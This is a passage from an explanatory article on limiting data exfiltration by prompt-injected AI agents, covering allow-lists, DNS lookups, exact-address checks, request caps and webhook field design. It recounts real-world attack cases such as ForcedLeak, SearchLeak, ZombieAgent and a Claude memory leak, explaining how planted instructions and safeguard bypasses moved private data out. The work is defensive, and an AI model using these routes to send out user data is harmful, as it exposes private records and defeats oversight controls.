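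An attacker who plants text in the supplier's page may never see the sales assistant's context, but if the company uses a commercial product, the attacker can probably also buy it and test wordings beforehand. By the time the employee asks for a summary, the attacker may already have a text that works most of the time. An average rate over older attacks is a poor guide to how often a text selected this way will succeed.

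The number of targets matters too. Suppose a planted instruction works once in every thousand readings. If a company's assistant reads five hostile pages a year, the chance of a theft is about 0.5% a year, which the company might accept for data of modest value. If assistants at many companies read such pages 100,000 times in total, the expected number of thefts is about 100. A vendor responsible for all those assistants has much less reason to accept the same rate.

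For private customer records, Willison's position is stronger, because a company can't retrieve a phone number from someone else's server the way it can correct a bad summary. A low attack success rate is still valuable, since it means the model stops many careless attacks and other defences are needed less often. But it doesn't justify giving the model unrestricted control of a web request.

### Designing for a model that someone has fooled

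OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) reaches a similar conclusion from experience with ChatGPT. OpenAI writes that most of the attacks it knows of try to make the assistant send secrets from a conversation to an outsider, and that most fail because the model's training leads it to refuse. It still recommends designing systems to limit the damage when an attack succeeds.

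Part of the reason is that the attacks have changed. Early ones gave the model a direct order, which newer models usually ignore. The most effective attacks now resemble social engineering, in which someone tricks a person into helping by inventing a plausible story. OpenAI cites an email, reported by outside researchers in 2025, that was written as a routine follow-up about a company reorganisation. In testing, it worked 50% of the time when the user asked ChatGPT to research that day's emails about a new employee process.

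Some companies sell "AI firewalls", which try to detect planted instructions before the model reads them. OpenAI says that these usually miss well-developed attacks. A filter would have to recognise a lie, often without the information needed to check it. For example, a thief and the personnel department could send identically worded emails asking for an employee's details.

OpenAI compares the model to a customer service worker who can give refunds. The employer trains the worker to recognise dishonest customers but expects some to succeed anyway, so it sets a maximum refund in the payment system. The worker cannot exceed that limit, however convincing the customer's story is. OpenAI recommends asking what limits a company would put on a person in the agent's position and building those limits into the software.

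For ChatGPT, OpenAI looks for combinations of a sink and a source, where a source is a way for an outsider to influence the model. For the sales assistant, the source is the supplier's page. The company cannot control what the supplier publishes, but it can decide which addresses the harness will contact and which facts a message may contain. Willison drew a similar lesson from the auto mode results and decided to put more effort into finding a practical way to run agents without access to data or tools that could cause harm if someone misled the agents.

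## Does it help to limit requests to approved sites?

A destination allow-list is the simplest limit that ordinary software can enforce, and it stopped every theft in Lan and colleagues' test. But between September 2025 and September 2026, researchers published at least five ways around the allow-lists in commercial products. In four of those five, the data left through a host the vendor had approved.

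### How the check works

Suppose the company lists the website hosts of its twelve suppliers. When the model writes a fetch, the harness handles it in this order:

1. Parse the address into its parts and take out the host.
2. Normalise the host, so that different spellings of one name compare as equal. For example, change capitals to lower case and remove a final dot.
3. Compare the whole host with the entries on the list, and refuse the request unless one of them matches.
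4. Look up the host's numeric address, and refuse the request if that address belongs to the company's internal network.
5. Connect to that numeric address and confirm that the server holds a valid certificate for the host.
6. If the server replies with a redirect to another address, go back to the beginning with the new address.

Small mistakes in this procedure can make it useless. If the harness searches the address for the text `supplier.example` instead of parsing it, it will accept `https://attacker.example/supplier.example`, where the supplier's name is only part of the path. The comparison has to come before the lookup, because the lookup itself discloses the host name. The harness should also connect to the numeric address it checked, since a second lookup may return a different one.

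Most software for fetching pages follows redirects automatically, so if a developer checks only the address the model wrote, an approved site can redirect the request to one that isn't approved. To prevent this, the developer has to turn off automatic redirects or check each new address before the software requests it.

The rule itself is short. If $h(u)$ is the host in the address $u$, and $L$ is the set of listed hosts, the harness sends the request only if

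$$h(u) \in L.$$

The harness checks only each request's destination against the list, so it doesn't have to inspect the path, query or message body for private data. A model that has followed a planted instruction may encode a phone number or split it across ten requests, but the harness refuses them all if the attacker's host isn't on the list.

For the same reason, the harness will send anything to a listed host. Suppose someone plants an instruction in a customer review on the supplier's page, and the model requests an address on the supplier's site that contains the phone number. The supplier now has a phone number it shouldn't have, but the reviewer can't read the supplier's server log and gains nothing. But if the attacker has taken over the supplier's server, the theft succeeds, because the list allows the request. Whoever writes the list therefore has to know who can read what arrives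 at each host, which is harder than knowing whether the site is respectable.

### Where the check can run

The company can put the check in several places, and each one covers different requests.

| Position | What it can see | What it misses |
|---|---|---|
| Code of the fetch tool | The full address and body, and which employee and task they belong to | Requests from other tools, from programs the model writes, and from the program displaying the reply |
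| Proxy around the sandbox | The host of every connection from the sandbox, and the full address if it decrypts the traffic | Anything that software outside the sandbox sends |
| Network firewall | Numeric addresses, and usually host names, for every machine on the network | The path and body of encrypted requests, and anything a vendor's servers send |
| Browser content policy | The images, scripts and other resources that a displayed page tries to load | Requests from the harness or from any server |

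A proxy is a program that other programs must send their requests through. A content security policy, or content policy for short, is a list a web server sends with a page, naming the hosts from which the browser may load images and other resources.

For the sales assistant, a check in the tool's code provides the most information about a request, because that code handles the request before it is encrypted. But the check protects only that tool. If the assistant can also run programs, the company needs a proxy around the sandbox, and if the assistant's replies can contain images, the company also needs a content policy. All four controls together would not have stopped the file-based attack in ReLeak, because Microsoft's own servers sent that request.

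### An approved domain can change hands

Salesforce sells software in which companies keep their customer records, and its Agentforce product lets AI agents work on those records. A standard feature called Web-to-Lead saves whatever a visitor types into a public web form as a new sales lead. In 2025, researchers at Noma Security used such a form to plant instructions in a lead. When an employee later asked Agentforce about that lead, the model added an image to its answer and put the email addresses of other leads in the image's URL. Noma called the attack ForcedLeak.

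Salesforce's content policy failed to block the image request because, according to Willison, it still approved every host under `my-salesforce-cms.com`, a domain whose registration had expired. Noma registered the domain. The browser then applied the policy correctly when it requested the image, and the lead data arrived in Noma's server logs. Salesforce Ben, a news site for Salesforce users, quotes Noma calling the expired domain "a trusted exfiltration channel".

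Salesforce took back the domain and corrected the policy. It also added a control called Trusted URLs, which prevents its agents from sending output to addresses outside an approved list (The Hacker News, 2025). Noma reported the flaw on 28 July 2025, Salesforce began enforcing Trusted URLs on 8 September, and the attack became public on 25 September (ThaiCERT, *ForcedLeak Vulnerability in Salesforce Agentforce Risks CRM Data Exposure via Prompt Injection*).

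An approved host name points to whoever holds the domain's registration today, who may not be the organisation the administrator meant to approve. Forgotten entries are common outside AI products too. The Hacker News' *An Abandoned CDN Domain Was Re-Registered. Thousands of Sites Still Call It* (2026) describes the same problem with a domain that once belonged to a content delivery network, a service that stores copies of files for other websites.

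Each entry therefore needs a named owner and a date on which it expires unless the owner renews it. Before renewing, the owner should confirm that the assistant still uses the host and that the same organisation still controls it. The expiry date matters more than the owner, since people leave companies and forget old entries. If a necessary entry expires by accident, someone will notice the failed fetch and complain, whereas an unnecessary entry can stay on the list unnoticed.

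The Salesforce entry was also a wildcard, with an asterisk covering every host under the domain. The wildcard didn't cause this leak, because the domain's new owner controlled all of its hosts and could have set up whichever one the policy named. Wildcards are still a bad idea because they include hosts that don't exist yet. Many hosting services give each customer a separate host under a shared domain, so a wildcard for that domain covers the host of anyone who opens an account.

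### An approved host can have the wrong readers

Google's Antigravity is a programming tool in which Gemini, Google's model, writes code and can open a web browser to test it. The browser has an allow-list of sites. In November 2025, PromptArmor's *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data* reported that the default list included Webhook.site, a public service where anyone can create an address and see the requests sent to it. Programmers use it to check what their software sends, which may be why it was on the list, but an attacker can also use it to collect stolen data.

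In PromptArmor's demonstration, a programmer gave Gemini a guide found online, and text hidden in the guide led the model to collect pieces of code and the keys to a cloud account. The model added them to a Webhook.site address and opened it in the browser. The list of approved sites allowed the request, and the testers read the keys in Webhook.site's log.

The same test showed that restricting one tool doesn't necessarily restrict the others. Antigravity's default settings stopped Gemini's usual file-reading tools from opening the file that held the keys, so Gemini printed the file with a terminal command. Willison wondered whether a terminal command could also have sent the data, which would have made the browser's list irrelevant. PromptArmor didn't test that in its write-up, but says it found three other ways to get data out without the browser tools.

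PromptArmor did not report the flaw privately before publishing because Google had already acknowledged the risk. Antigravity warned new users about data exfiltration, and Google listed the problem among its known issues. Google said it was working on a fix, but PromptArmor does not report one. The entry would be easy to remove from the list of approved sites, which users can open with a button in the settings.

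A company can avoid this kind of mistake by starting with an empty list and adding only the hosts its own tasks need, instead of accepting the vendor's generic default. Before adding a host, it should check whether a stranger with a free account could read any of what the assistant sends there. Public forums, file-sharing sites and web form builders all fail this test, even when their owners are reputable.

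The test gets harder when one host serves many customers and keeps their data apart. Claude Cowork, Anthropic's agent for general office work, runs programs in a virtual machine (a simulated computer isolated from the real one) that blocks connections to almost every domain. One exception was Anthropic's API, through which other programs use the company's models and store files. Two days after Anthropic released Cowork in January 2026, PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* showed that this exception was enough to leak files.

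A user connected a folder of property files and uploaded a document with hidden instructions, which included a key to the attacker's Anthropic account. The model used the key to upload one of the user's files, which contained financial figures and parts of social security numbers, and nobody had to approve the upload. Anthropic's server stored the file in the attacker's account, as it would for any customer with a valid key.

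PromptArmor carried out this attack on Claude Haiku. In another test, it got the more resistant Opus 4.5 to upload customer records through the same route. Rehberger had found the underlying flaw in Claude's chat product before Cowork existed, and Anthropic had acknowledged it but not fixed it. Anthropic was deploying an update to Cowork's virtual machine by 16 January, according to *Anthropic Claude Vulnerability Exposes Cowork AI to Data Exfiltration via Prompt Injection* (Apostol, 2026).

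If Cowork needed the API to work, no choice of hosts would have solved this. The missing rule was a limit on which account could receive uploads. A proxy can enforce such a rule by removing any key the model supplies and inserting the company's own, so that an upload can only go to the company's account. This is called account binding, and it requires either a proxy that decrypts the request or a check in the tool's code, because a firewall that sees only the host name can't distinguish one customer's upload from another's.

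Many ordinary business services have the same structure. The sales team's chat service probably uses one host for the webhooks of every company that uses it, and the rest of the address determines whose chat receives the message. Approving the whole host would let the model post a customer's record in a stranger's chat, so an administrator should set the complete webhook address.

### An approved host can pass the request on

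OpenAI's first objection to lists of trusted sites is that many legitimate sites redirect visitors elsewhere, so if the software checks only the first domain, an attacker can sometimes route a request through a trusted site to their own server. Some sites have a page that redirects to whatever address appears in its query, for instance to count clicks on outgoing links. That address can contain the private data.

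Checking every redirect against the list of approved sites answers this objection almost completely. A redirect comes back to the software that made the original request, which must make a second request to follow it. If the new host isn't on the list, the software doesn't send that request, so the data reaches the redirecting site but not the attacker.

The check can't be repeated on a second address if the approved host fetches that address itself. In June 2026, Taler described SearchLeak, an attack on the search feature of Microsoft 365 Copilot that began when an employee clicked a link to Microsoft's own site. Copilot treated the search query in the link as an instruction. The model searched the employee's mailbox and wrote an answer containing an image whose address included the subject line of an email.

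Microsoft had two defences at this point, and both failed. The first converted any image code in an answer to plain text, but only after the model had finished writing. The browser displayed the answer as it arrived and requested the image before the conversion. The second defence, the content policy, would have blocked an image from the attacker's host, but it approved every host under `bing.com`, and Bing has a feature that accepts the address of an image and fetches it for analysis. The browser contacted Bing, as the policy allowed, and one of Bing's servers, which the policy doesn't govern, then contacted the attacker's host.

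Microsoft rated the flaw critical and fixed it on its own servers. The Next Web's *A single click on a Microsoft link could have drained your inbox* notes that the flaw scored only 6.5 out of 10 on the industry's common severity scale, because the employee had to click a link. Microsoft found no evidence that anyone had used the flaw maliciously.

Fixing one forwarding route has not prevented leaks through others. EchoLeak used a Teams service in the same way in 2025, and months after SearchLeak, Simonovich and his colleagues at Cato got data out through Bing again. Microsoft missed these routes even though it owns all the services involved, so an outside company is unlikely to find every such feature on a large site.

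Taler advises companies to review their content policies and to treat any approved domain that fetches web addresses for its users, such as a translation service, link preview or image resizer, as a possible way to leak data. Approving a specific host instead of a whole domain can help. If Copilot needed images from only one Bing host, Microsoft could have listed that host alone, which might have excluded the image search. But small hosts with a single purpose are safer. People tend to approve large, famous sites first because they trust the owner, yet those sites have the most features, and an attacker needs only one feature that forwards a request or shows it to strangers.

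### Data can leave around the list

Salesforce introduced Trusted URLs in response to ForcedLeak, and a year later researchers at Zenity Labs announced that they had bypassed it. Their attack, SalesBleed, also began with an instruction planted through a Web-to-Lead form. In the demonstration, Agentforce disclosed company names, deal sizes and email addresses.

This time the list contained no bad entry. Antipov (2026), in *Один вредоносный лид против всей CRM*, reports that the check mishandled certain domain endings and special character sequences. It therefore failed while reading addresses, before comparing them with the list. The browser then loaded an image from an address that Trusted URLs should have removed. In a second version of the attack, the data left through a link preview in Slack.

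Poireault (2026), in *Vulnerabilities in Salesforce Agentforce Expose Wider AI Agent Risk*, says instead that the data left by "DNS-based exfiltration techniques", that is, through host-name lookups. The two accounts can both be true if the data was in the host name of the image's address.

Agentforce sometimes showed the employee a message saying that security policy had blocked the content, even though the request had already gone out. In SearchLeak, too, the protective step came after the browser had acted. A notice that something was blocked is therefore poor evidence that no data left. To find out, an administrator has to check the network traffic, including DNS lookups.

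Zenity reported the flaws on 1 June 2026. Poireault dates the repair of the link check to 18 August, while 三村 (2026), in *Salesforce Agentforceの「SalesBleed」脆弱性*, says Zenity confirmed it on 19 August and confirmed the last of the related Slack fixes on 21 September. No public document shows that anyone exploited the flaws. 三村 adds that Trusted URLs only limits where the results can go and was never meant to prevent prompt injection, so an agent can still follow a planted instruction after the repair.

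*Cracks in the Bedrock* (Hadad, 2026) showed that DNS lookups could also carry data out of the sandbox Amazon offers for AI agents. An administrator can easily overlook this because blocking a program's connections doesn't necessarily block its lookups.

The remedy is to give the sandbox no DNS resolver. A program inside it passes the host name to the proxy, which looks the name up only if it is on the list. Exact entries matter here too, because a wildcard lets the model put its own text in front of the domain, and whoever runs that domain's name servers will receive it. With twelve exact entries, the model can choose only which of twelve names to look up, so each choice conveys at most $\log_2 12$, or about 3.6, bits.

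None of this helps with an image in a displayed reply, because the employee's browser does its own lookups. The harness therefore has to remove links and images that point to unlisted hosts before any part of the reply reaches the browser. It also has to parse addresses exactly as the browser does, or an address that passes the check may still lead to an outside host.

### When a closed list is practical

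OpenAI's other objection is that a strict list trains people to click through warnings without thinking. Users don't visit only a handful of famous sites, so the list produces frequent warnings about harmless pages. An employee who has approved forty harmless suppliers' sites this month will probably approve the forty-first too.

This is a good argument against a list that the employee can override. It is weaker against a closed list, where the harness refuses unlisted hosts and the employee can't override the refusal. The employee can ask an administrator to add the host, and the administrator can check it without being in the middle of the task. But the task fails until someone adds the host. If that happens every day, employees will paste the records into another assistant that has no restrictions, and the company will be worse off than before.

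A closed list is practical when the assistant needs few hosts and the company can name them in advance. It may suit the sales assistant if staff ask only about the company's twelve suppliers. The administrator could enter each supplier's exact host, make the supplier's account manager responsible for the entry, and set it to expire when the supply contract ends. To check whether the list would cover what employees need, the company can first record the hosts they ask for, without giving the assistant access to customer records, and see whether new ones stop appearing after a few weeks.

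Programming agents mostly need a few well-known hosts, such as public code repositories. But many of those hosts also accept uploads from anyone with an account, as Anthropic's API did, so the company would have to restrict what the agent can do there, for example by allowing downloads and blocking uploads. A download request can still carry private data in its address, but this helps an attacker only if they can read the host's records of the request.

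A list of approved sites doesn't work for an assistant that researches arbitrary questions on the open web. Nobody can predict which sites will have the answer, and a list long enough to be useful would include many sites that forward requests or let strangers read them. OpenAI faced this problem with ChatGPT and decided that whether a domain "seems reputable" was the wrong test for automatic fetching.

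## Can software check the exact address instead of the site?

OpenAI chose to check whether the complete address already existed in a source the model did not write. If an address was public before the employee typed anything, it is unlikely to contain a phone number that the assistant has just read in a customer's record. The harness can apply this test without judging the site's reputation or recognising a phone number.

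Let $K$ be the set of addresses the harness knows from such sources. A site list compares only the host of an address $u$ with its entries. The exact-address check compares all of it, and the harness sends the request only if

$$u \in K.$$

Suppose the instructions planted in the supplier's page are to fetch an address ending in the customer's phone number. The software allows the fetch only if that exact address is already in $K$. The attacker doesn't know the number, so they would need ten billion addresses in $K$ to cover every ten-digit number.

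SearchLeak got past a site list by putting private data in an image address on an approved Bing host. An exact-address check would have refused that address before the browser contacted Bing, because no outside source would have recorded an address containing the subject line of a private email. For the same reason, it would refuse an address that carried private data through a redirect page on a respectable site.

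For this to work, the harness has to compare the host, path and query, and can safely ignore only the fragment. The same article often appears under several addresses that differ only in a tracking code. Ignoring the query would make these addresses match, but it would also let the model write anything after the question mark.

### OpenAI's public index

OpenAI builds its index of known addresses with a crawler, a program that scans public web pages and records the addresses it finds, as a search engine does. Before ChatGPT automatically loads a page or an image, software looks up the full address in this index. If the address is there, ChatGPT loads the page or image. Otherwise, the software either tells the agent to try a different website or warns the user that the link is unverified and may contain information from the conversation. The warning displays the address, but it protects only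 users who read it.

The crawler has no access to users' conversations or accounts. This separation is essential because if the index also included addresses that users opened, it could contain a private address that one person visited, and the check would treat that address as public.

The index has an exception for addresses that users supply. Johann Rehberger, the researcher who later broke Claude Code's auto mode, reviewed OpenAI's technical paper on the design in *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, a post on his blog Embrace The Red. As he understands it, ChatGPT treats an address as safe for the rest of a chat if the user typed it in a message. Without this exception, the employee could not get a summary of a page that the crawler had missed.

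OpenAI promises only that the agent won't quietly leak a user's data through the address itself. A page in the index can still contain planted instructions. In the sales example, such a page could lead the model to put the phone number in the webhook's message, which this check doesn't examine.

### Anthropic's rule about the conversation

Anthropic released a fetch tool for developers in September 2025 with a rule that needs no index of the web. The harness searches the conversation for the address and refuses the fetch if it isn't there. Willison (2025), in *Claude API*, quotes the original documentation's statement that Claude "is not allowed to dynamically construct URLs". He thought this part of the rule gave the most protection, because attackers usually tell the model to build an address out of private data.

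The current version of the rule, in Anthropic's *Web fetch 工具*, accepts an address from three sources:

- the user's messages
- results from tools that the developer's own software runs
- results of earlier web searches and fetches

The harness refuses an address that appears only in the model's own output or in the developer's standing instructions. It also refuses an address that comes only from certain other tools on Anthropic's servers, including the tool that runs programs. A program the model wrote can print any address, so its output is no more independent of the model than the model's reply is.

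A developer's own tools can have the same problem. By default, the harness trusts their results even when a result repeats text the model wrote, as when an error message quotes the command that failed. An address the model composed can then appear in the conversation as though it came from outside. Anthropic's documentation mentions this and describes a setting that excludes any of the three sources, or particular tools within the last two.

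The developer can list either the tools to trust or the tools to exclude. Listing the trusted tools is safer because the harness then ignores any tool the developer adds later. With an exclusion list, the harness trusts each new tool until someone excludes it.

Willison found a weakness in the first source too. The rule accepts addresses from "user messages", but in many applications the developer's software pastes emails or documents into the same message as the user's request. If the sales assistant worked this way, a link that a customer typed into a comments field would count as an address from the employee. The company can avoid this by passing records to the model only as tool results and excluding the tool that returns them.

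Even if an address passes, the harness refuses it if it is longer than 250 characters or seems to contain a password or access key, unless the user or the developer put that key in the conversation. The key check would matter for links like those in the Copilot Cowork test, where anyone with the address could download a file, but only if the harness detected the key.

An earlier edition of Anthropic's *Web fetch tool* documentation warned that some risk of exfiltration remained even with the rule, and told developers to use the tool only in trusted environments or with data that isn't sensitive. If they were still concerned, it suggested disabling the tool, capping the number of fetches or restricting the domains. By that standard, the rule alone isn't enough protection for an assistant with customer records and open web access.

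### Which requests each design refuses

OpenAI's check requires an address to be public, while Anthropic's requires only that the address entered the conversation from a source other than the model. The two checks would apply to the sales assistant as follows.

| Address the assistant wants to fetch | OpenAI's check | Anthropic's developer tool, default settings |
|---|---|---|
| The employee typed it | Fetches it | Fetches it |
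| A web search returned it | Fetches it if the index has it | Fetches it |
| A page the assistant has just read links to it | Fetches it if the index has it | Fetches it |
| A private link in an email that the company's mail tool returned | Warns the user or tries another source | Fetches it |
| The model composed it to search a supplier's catalogue | Warns the user or tries another source | Refuses it |

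Losing catalogue searches is a real drawback. An employee might reasonably ask for the price of a part, and on many sites the only way to look it up is to put the part number in the address. Neither check can distinguish a part number from a phone number. A developer who needs such lookups can write a separate tool that accepts only a part number in a fixed format and builds the address itself.

OpenAI's check also refuses pages that a crawler can't find, such as a page published an hour ago or a document shared by private link. A lot of business material is like this. Anthropic's default handles such pages better, but it lets whoever wrote the email or page choose which addresses become permitted.

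A developer can combine an exact-address rule with a site list. Anthropic's tool has a setting for permitted domains, which Willison considers much stronger than the rule about the conversation, provided nobody can use those domains to exfiltrate data. He calls that condition "tricky", and the failures of approved domains at Salesforce and Microsoft support him. If the sales assistant used both, the model could open only known addresses on the twelve suppliers' sites, so it could no longer write data into an address there.

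### Choosing among permitted addresses

With either design, the model can still reveal information through its choice of address. The agent in *AgentTell* revealed its user's subscription by opening the Premium help guide, and an exact-address check would have approved that request.

Defenders can put an upper limit on this leak. The unit is the bit, the information in the answer to one question with two equally likely answers. If the harness permits $m$ addresses and the model makes $k$ requests, it can produce $m^k$ different sequences. Someone who sees the whole sequence can distinguish at most that many possibilities, so the sequence carries at most

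$$\log_2(m^k) = k\log_2 m \text{ bits.}$$

A random ten-digit number contains about 33 bits. With 1,000 permitted addresses, each request carries at most about 10 bits, so a cap of three requests keeps the total below 33 bits. A cap of twenty allows almost 200 bits, enough for six such numbers. Doubling the number of permitted addresses adds only one bit per request, while doubling the number of requests doubles the total. A company that can't shorten its list of addresses can still substantially reduce how much data can leak by limiting requests.

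$m$ should count only the addresses whose requests the attacker can observe, plus one for all other addresses combined. If the attacker owns a single site, requests to all other sites look the same to them. This is another reason to choose permitted hosts by who can read their logs.

The formula counts only which addresses the model opens, but a server can observe more. *Actions Speak Louder than Words* (2026) describes a site that offers one link for each of four tasks an agent might be working on, so that one request reveals the task. The formula accounts for this leak, which is $\log_2 4 = 2$ bits. But the paper also infers the task from how long an agent waited before its next request and how much of a file it downloaded. A cap on requests limits these signals but does not remove them.

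Some leakage remains even with a single permitted address. *An Application-Layer Multi-Modal Covert-Channel Reference Monitor for LLM Agent Egress* (2026) notes that the agent's choice to send something or stay silent always leaks one bit. For outgoing images, the paper's defence rounds average brightness to one of eight levels, so brightness can carry at most three bits per image. It also limits the total rate across a series of images. The paper claims only that the defence bounds the leak.

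These limits help protect long secrets such as access keys and phone numbers, but they do much less for short facts. Whether a customer is about to cancel, for example, is a yes-or-no question, and no limit that still allows a request can guarantee that the answer won't leak.

Anthropic's tool lets a developer cap the number of fetches, but it has no default cap. The cap applies to a single turn, which is everything the model does in response to one message from the user. The count restarts with each message, so the total for a long conversation can be many times the cap. A company that chooses its cap using the formula should have the harness count fetches across the whole conversation. If planted text can persist between conversations, for instance in the assistant's memory, even a cap on the whole conversation allows too many fetches.

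### ZombieAgent

Researchers have used this remaining channel against both companies' products. The security company Radware (2026) announced the first of these attacks, which it called ZombieAgent, on 8 January 2026. It worked against ChatGPT when the user had connected an email account or another outside service.

Radware's *ZombieAgent* reports that ChatGPT at the time would open an address only exactly as someone had provided it, which stopped earlier attacks in which the model attached private data to an address. Radware's researchers planted an email containing a set of ready-made addresses. When the user asked ChatGPT to do something with their mail, the model read the email and, without altering any address, leaked private data through its choice of which ones to open.

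The requests came from OpenAI's servers, so the user's computer and network couldn't block them. Radware told OpenAI on 29 September 2025 that an improved version of the attack had succeeded every time, but it doesn't say how many attempts it made.

ChatGPT also would not open an attacker's address stored in its memory, the notes it keeps about a user between chats. Radware found that a planted note could instead send the model back to an email containing the addresses. As with Anthropic's error messages, an address the harness would have refused from one source could arrive through another that it accepted. A developer has to consider every way the model can bring text into the conversation, including by rereading old material.

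Radware first reported the attack on 26 September 2025, and OpenAI fixed it on 16 December. SecurityWeek's *‘ZombieAgent’ Attack Let Researchers Take Over ChatGPT* gives the same date for the fix, but neither account explains what OpenAI changed. OpenAI published its description of the public index six weeks after the fix. An index would make this attack harder, because the attacker could no longer just invent a set of addresses and email them; a crawler would have to find the pages first.

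### Paul's attack on Claude

The second case concerned the consumer Claude app, which had a rule similar to the one in Anthropic's developer tool. In *The Memory Heist*, Paul (2026) tried to extract the information about him in Claude's memory. The app adds a summary of the user's recent conversations to every new one, and the model can also search older conversations. The model can therefore access private data even in a chat where the user has shared none.

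Paul first asked Claude to open an address that contained his name, on his own server, and the harness refused. He found that the app accepted addresses from the user's message, from search results and from links on pages it had already fetched. The links were the weak source, because a page's owner chooses them. A server can also create new links each time someone opens a page, so an attacker can keep adding permitted addresses during the conversation.

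Paul used a site built around such links to get Claude to disclose his name, home town and employer through the sequence of pages it opened. Simple planted instructions didn't work reliably, so Paul had to invent a plausible reason for Claude to cooperate. Willison (2026), in *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets*, adds that the site showed its hostile text only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude, so an employee who opened the page to check it would have seen nothing wrong.

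The links on Paul's site technically followed the rule because the model had not written them, but they violated the principle behind it because the attacker wrote them, some after the conversation had started. OpenAI's index excludes such links unless the crawler has already recorded them.

In response, Anthropic stopped the app's fetch tool from following links in the pages it fetches. Anthropic said its staff had already identified the problem, so it paid Paul no reward. According to Willison, the app can now fetch only addresses that the user enters or that a web search returns. This is close to OpenAI's design, since a page normally has to be in a search engine's index before a search can return it. The restriction also makes the app less useful. If the supplier's product page links to a technical data sheet, Claude has to find the sheet by searching, or the user has to paste its address.

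A fix in the app doesn't necessarily change the developer tool, which still accepts links from fetched pages by default. A company that builds its sales assistant on the tool can remove this source of addresses by changing the setting so that, among Anthropic's own tools, only web search can supply them.

### Caching and repeat visits

Rehberger calls OpenAI's public index "a significant improvement" but says the problem isn't solved. In 2023, he had described how a model can leak data through its choice among fixed addresses, and he says OpenAI's paper acknowledges this channel. The index doesn't remove it, because anyone who runs a large website probably already has plenty of pages in the index.

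He proposes two limits. The harness could keep a copy of each page for a few minutes and use it if the model requests the page again, so that the site receives only the first request. Or it could refuse to open the same full address twice in one session. Both prevent an attacker from reusing a small set of addresses. Keeping a copy disrupts legitimate tasks less, since an agent can still reread a page.

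The formula gives an estimate of how much this would help. Suppose an attacker can observe twelve addresses and the model makes twelve requests. With repeats, the model can send up to 43 bits. If each address works only once, the model can only choose the order of the twelve, and the limit falls to $\log_2(12!)$, or about 29 bits. No addresses are left after that, whereas with repeats the total would keep growing. But if the attacker can observe 1,000 addresses and the model makes five requests, the limit is about 50 bits either way. A rule against repeats therefore helps most when the attacker can observe few addresses, and a company still needs a cap on requests for cases where the attacker can observe many.

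Rehberger had not tested ChatGPT recently, so Embrace The Red doesn't establish whether it already had such limits. Anthropic's fetch tool keeps copies of pages to save time and avoid redundant requests. Newer versions let the caller bypass the copy to get fresh content, and Anthropic says the caching may change over time. A developer who wants caching to work as a security limit has to enforce it in the harness.

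### Every place that sends a request

Rehberger's remaining concern is that a company's own developers may not know about a safeguard or may forget to use it. He has seen this happen with ChatGPT. He reported the leak through images to OpenAI in early 2023, and that December OpenAI added a first check on whether an address was safe. It did not explain the check's criteria, and the ChatGPT apps for Mac and iPhone lacked it. Rehberger also found ways around the check where OpenAI did apply it. Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* showed that a hostile document could use one of them to send a user's past chats to an outside server. OpenAI strengthened the check around August 2025.

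By March 2026, OpenAI was calling the mechanism Safe Url and had listed where it applied. In the Atlas browser, it covers the pages the agent opens and the bookmarks it creates. In Deep Research, which writes long reports from many web sources, it covers searches and page visits. Small applications that ChatGPT builds or runs for a user have a similar protection that uses a sandbox to detect unexpected communication and ask for consent.

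A company can test whether a product applies the basic rule by asking the model to open a made-up address on the company's own server and then checking the server's log. It should repeat the test in every app and with every tool that can send a request. Willison did a test like this on the Claude app in September 2025, and the app correctly refused to open an address the model had composed. Paul's attack worked ten months later because it used only addresses the model had been given, so a company also needs to test which sources can supply addresses.

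## How should a webhook's destination and fields be fixed?

A webhook needs a different design from a fetch because the company wants it to carry private data. The company therefore has to decide which data may go to which recipient.

For this note, the sales team may see a customer's name and products but not the phone number, and the supplier may see none of these. If $P$ is the set of permitted pairs of data and recipient, a message to recipient $r$ is acceptable only if

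$$(c, r) \in P$$

for every category of data $c$ in the message. Ordinary software can enforce much of this policy, provided the developer leaves the model few arguments to fill in.

### A tool that can send anything

The quickest way to connect the assistant to the team's chat is to give it a general tool for sending web requests. The tool's schema, the description of its arguments that the harness gives the model, would have one argument for the address and another for the body. The developer would put the webhook's address in the standing instructions and tell the model to post notes there.

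Normally, the model reads the supplier's page, copies the webhook's address into the call and writes a note, and the harness sends it. But if the page contains a planted instruction, the model can use the same tool to send the whole customer record to a stranger's server, and the harness will treat that call as equally valid.

Microsoft (2026) lists raw web requests among ten common mistakes it sees in agents that companies build. People often copy a sample request or use one for testing, then leave it in the finished agent. Microsoft recommends connectors instead, which are ready-made integrations with a particular service that add identity checks and usage limits. Administrators can also allow the raw request tool during development and block it in agents that staff use.

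### The administrator sets the destination

Some chat services already tie a webhook to one destination. According to Slack's *Sending messages using incoming webhooks*, the person who installs the webhook picks a channel, and Slack creates an address that posts only there. The message can't change the channel or the sender's displayed name.

For its older webhooks, however, Slack documents a `channel` field in the message body that overrides the channel chosen at installation. If the model writes the whole body, it can redirect the note even though the harness holds the address. The harness should therefore build the body itself and take only the note's text from the model.

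If a service doesn't fix the destination, the builder often can. Zapier, whose software connects thousands of applications, allows this on its server for the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for offering tools to AI agents. For each field, the builder can set one value, give the model a list to choose from, or let the model write the value. An older Zapier guide gives an example much like the sales assistant, in which the builder fixes the Slack channel and the model writes only the message text. The guide's reason was that models sometimes guess wrong, so fixing a field is useful even when there is no attacker.

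The builder often has to turn this protection on. In Copilot Studio, a workflow's inputs are set to "Dynamically fill with AI" by default, according to Microsoft's *Add Copilot Studio workflows as tools to agents*. To fix a destination that is one of those inputs, the builder has to change its setting to a custom value.

A fixed value must also override whatever the model writes. Merge's *Tool input overrides* describes a product that replaces the model's value just before the call is sent, so every message goes to the chosen Slack workspace even if the model names another. A default that applies only when the model leaves the field empty would give no protection, since a misled model can fill it in.

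### The harness keeps the address and its key

A Slack webhook address contains a secret, and anyone who has the address can post to the channel. If the address appears in the model's standing instructions, a planted instruction could lead the model to disclose it. An outsider could then post convincing messages to the sales team long after the conversation ended. Slack searches for leaked addresses and revokes them, but it may not find one that was sent to a private server.

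The harness should keep the address in a secret store and add it after the model has written the call. Microsoft gives similar advice about access keys, which it often finds written directly into an agent's configuration, where others can read and copy them.

It is also better to leave a fixed field out of the schema. With Merge's overrides, the model still sees the field and can fill it in, but Merge discards the value. The model might then tell the employee that it posted to a channel it never reached. Camunda's workflow software avoids this by including only the fields that the builder marks for the model, as Camunda's *AI agent tool definitions* explains.

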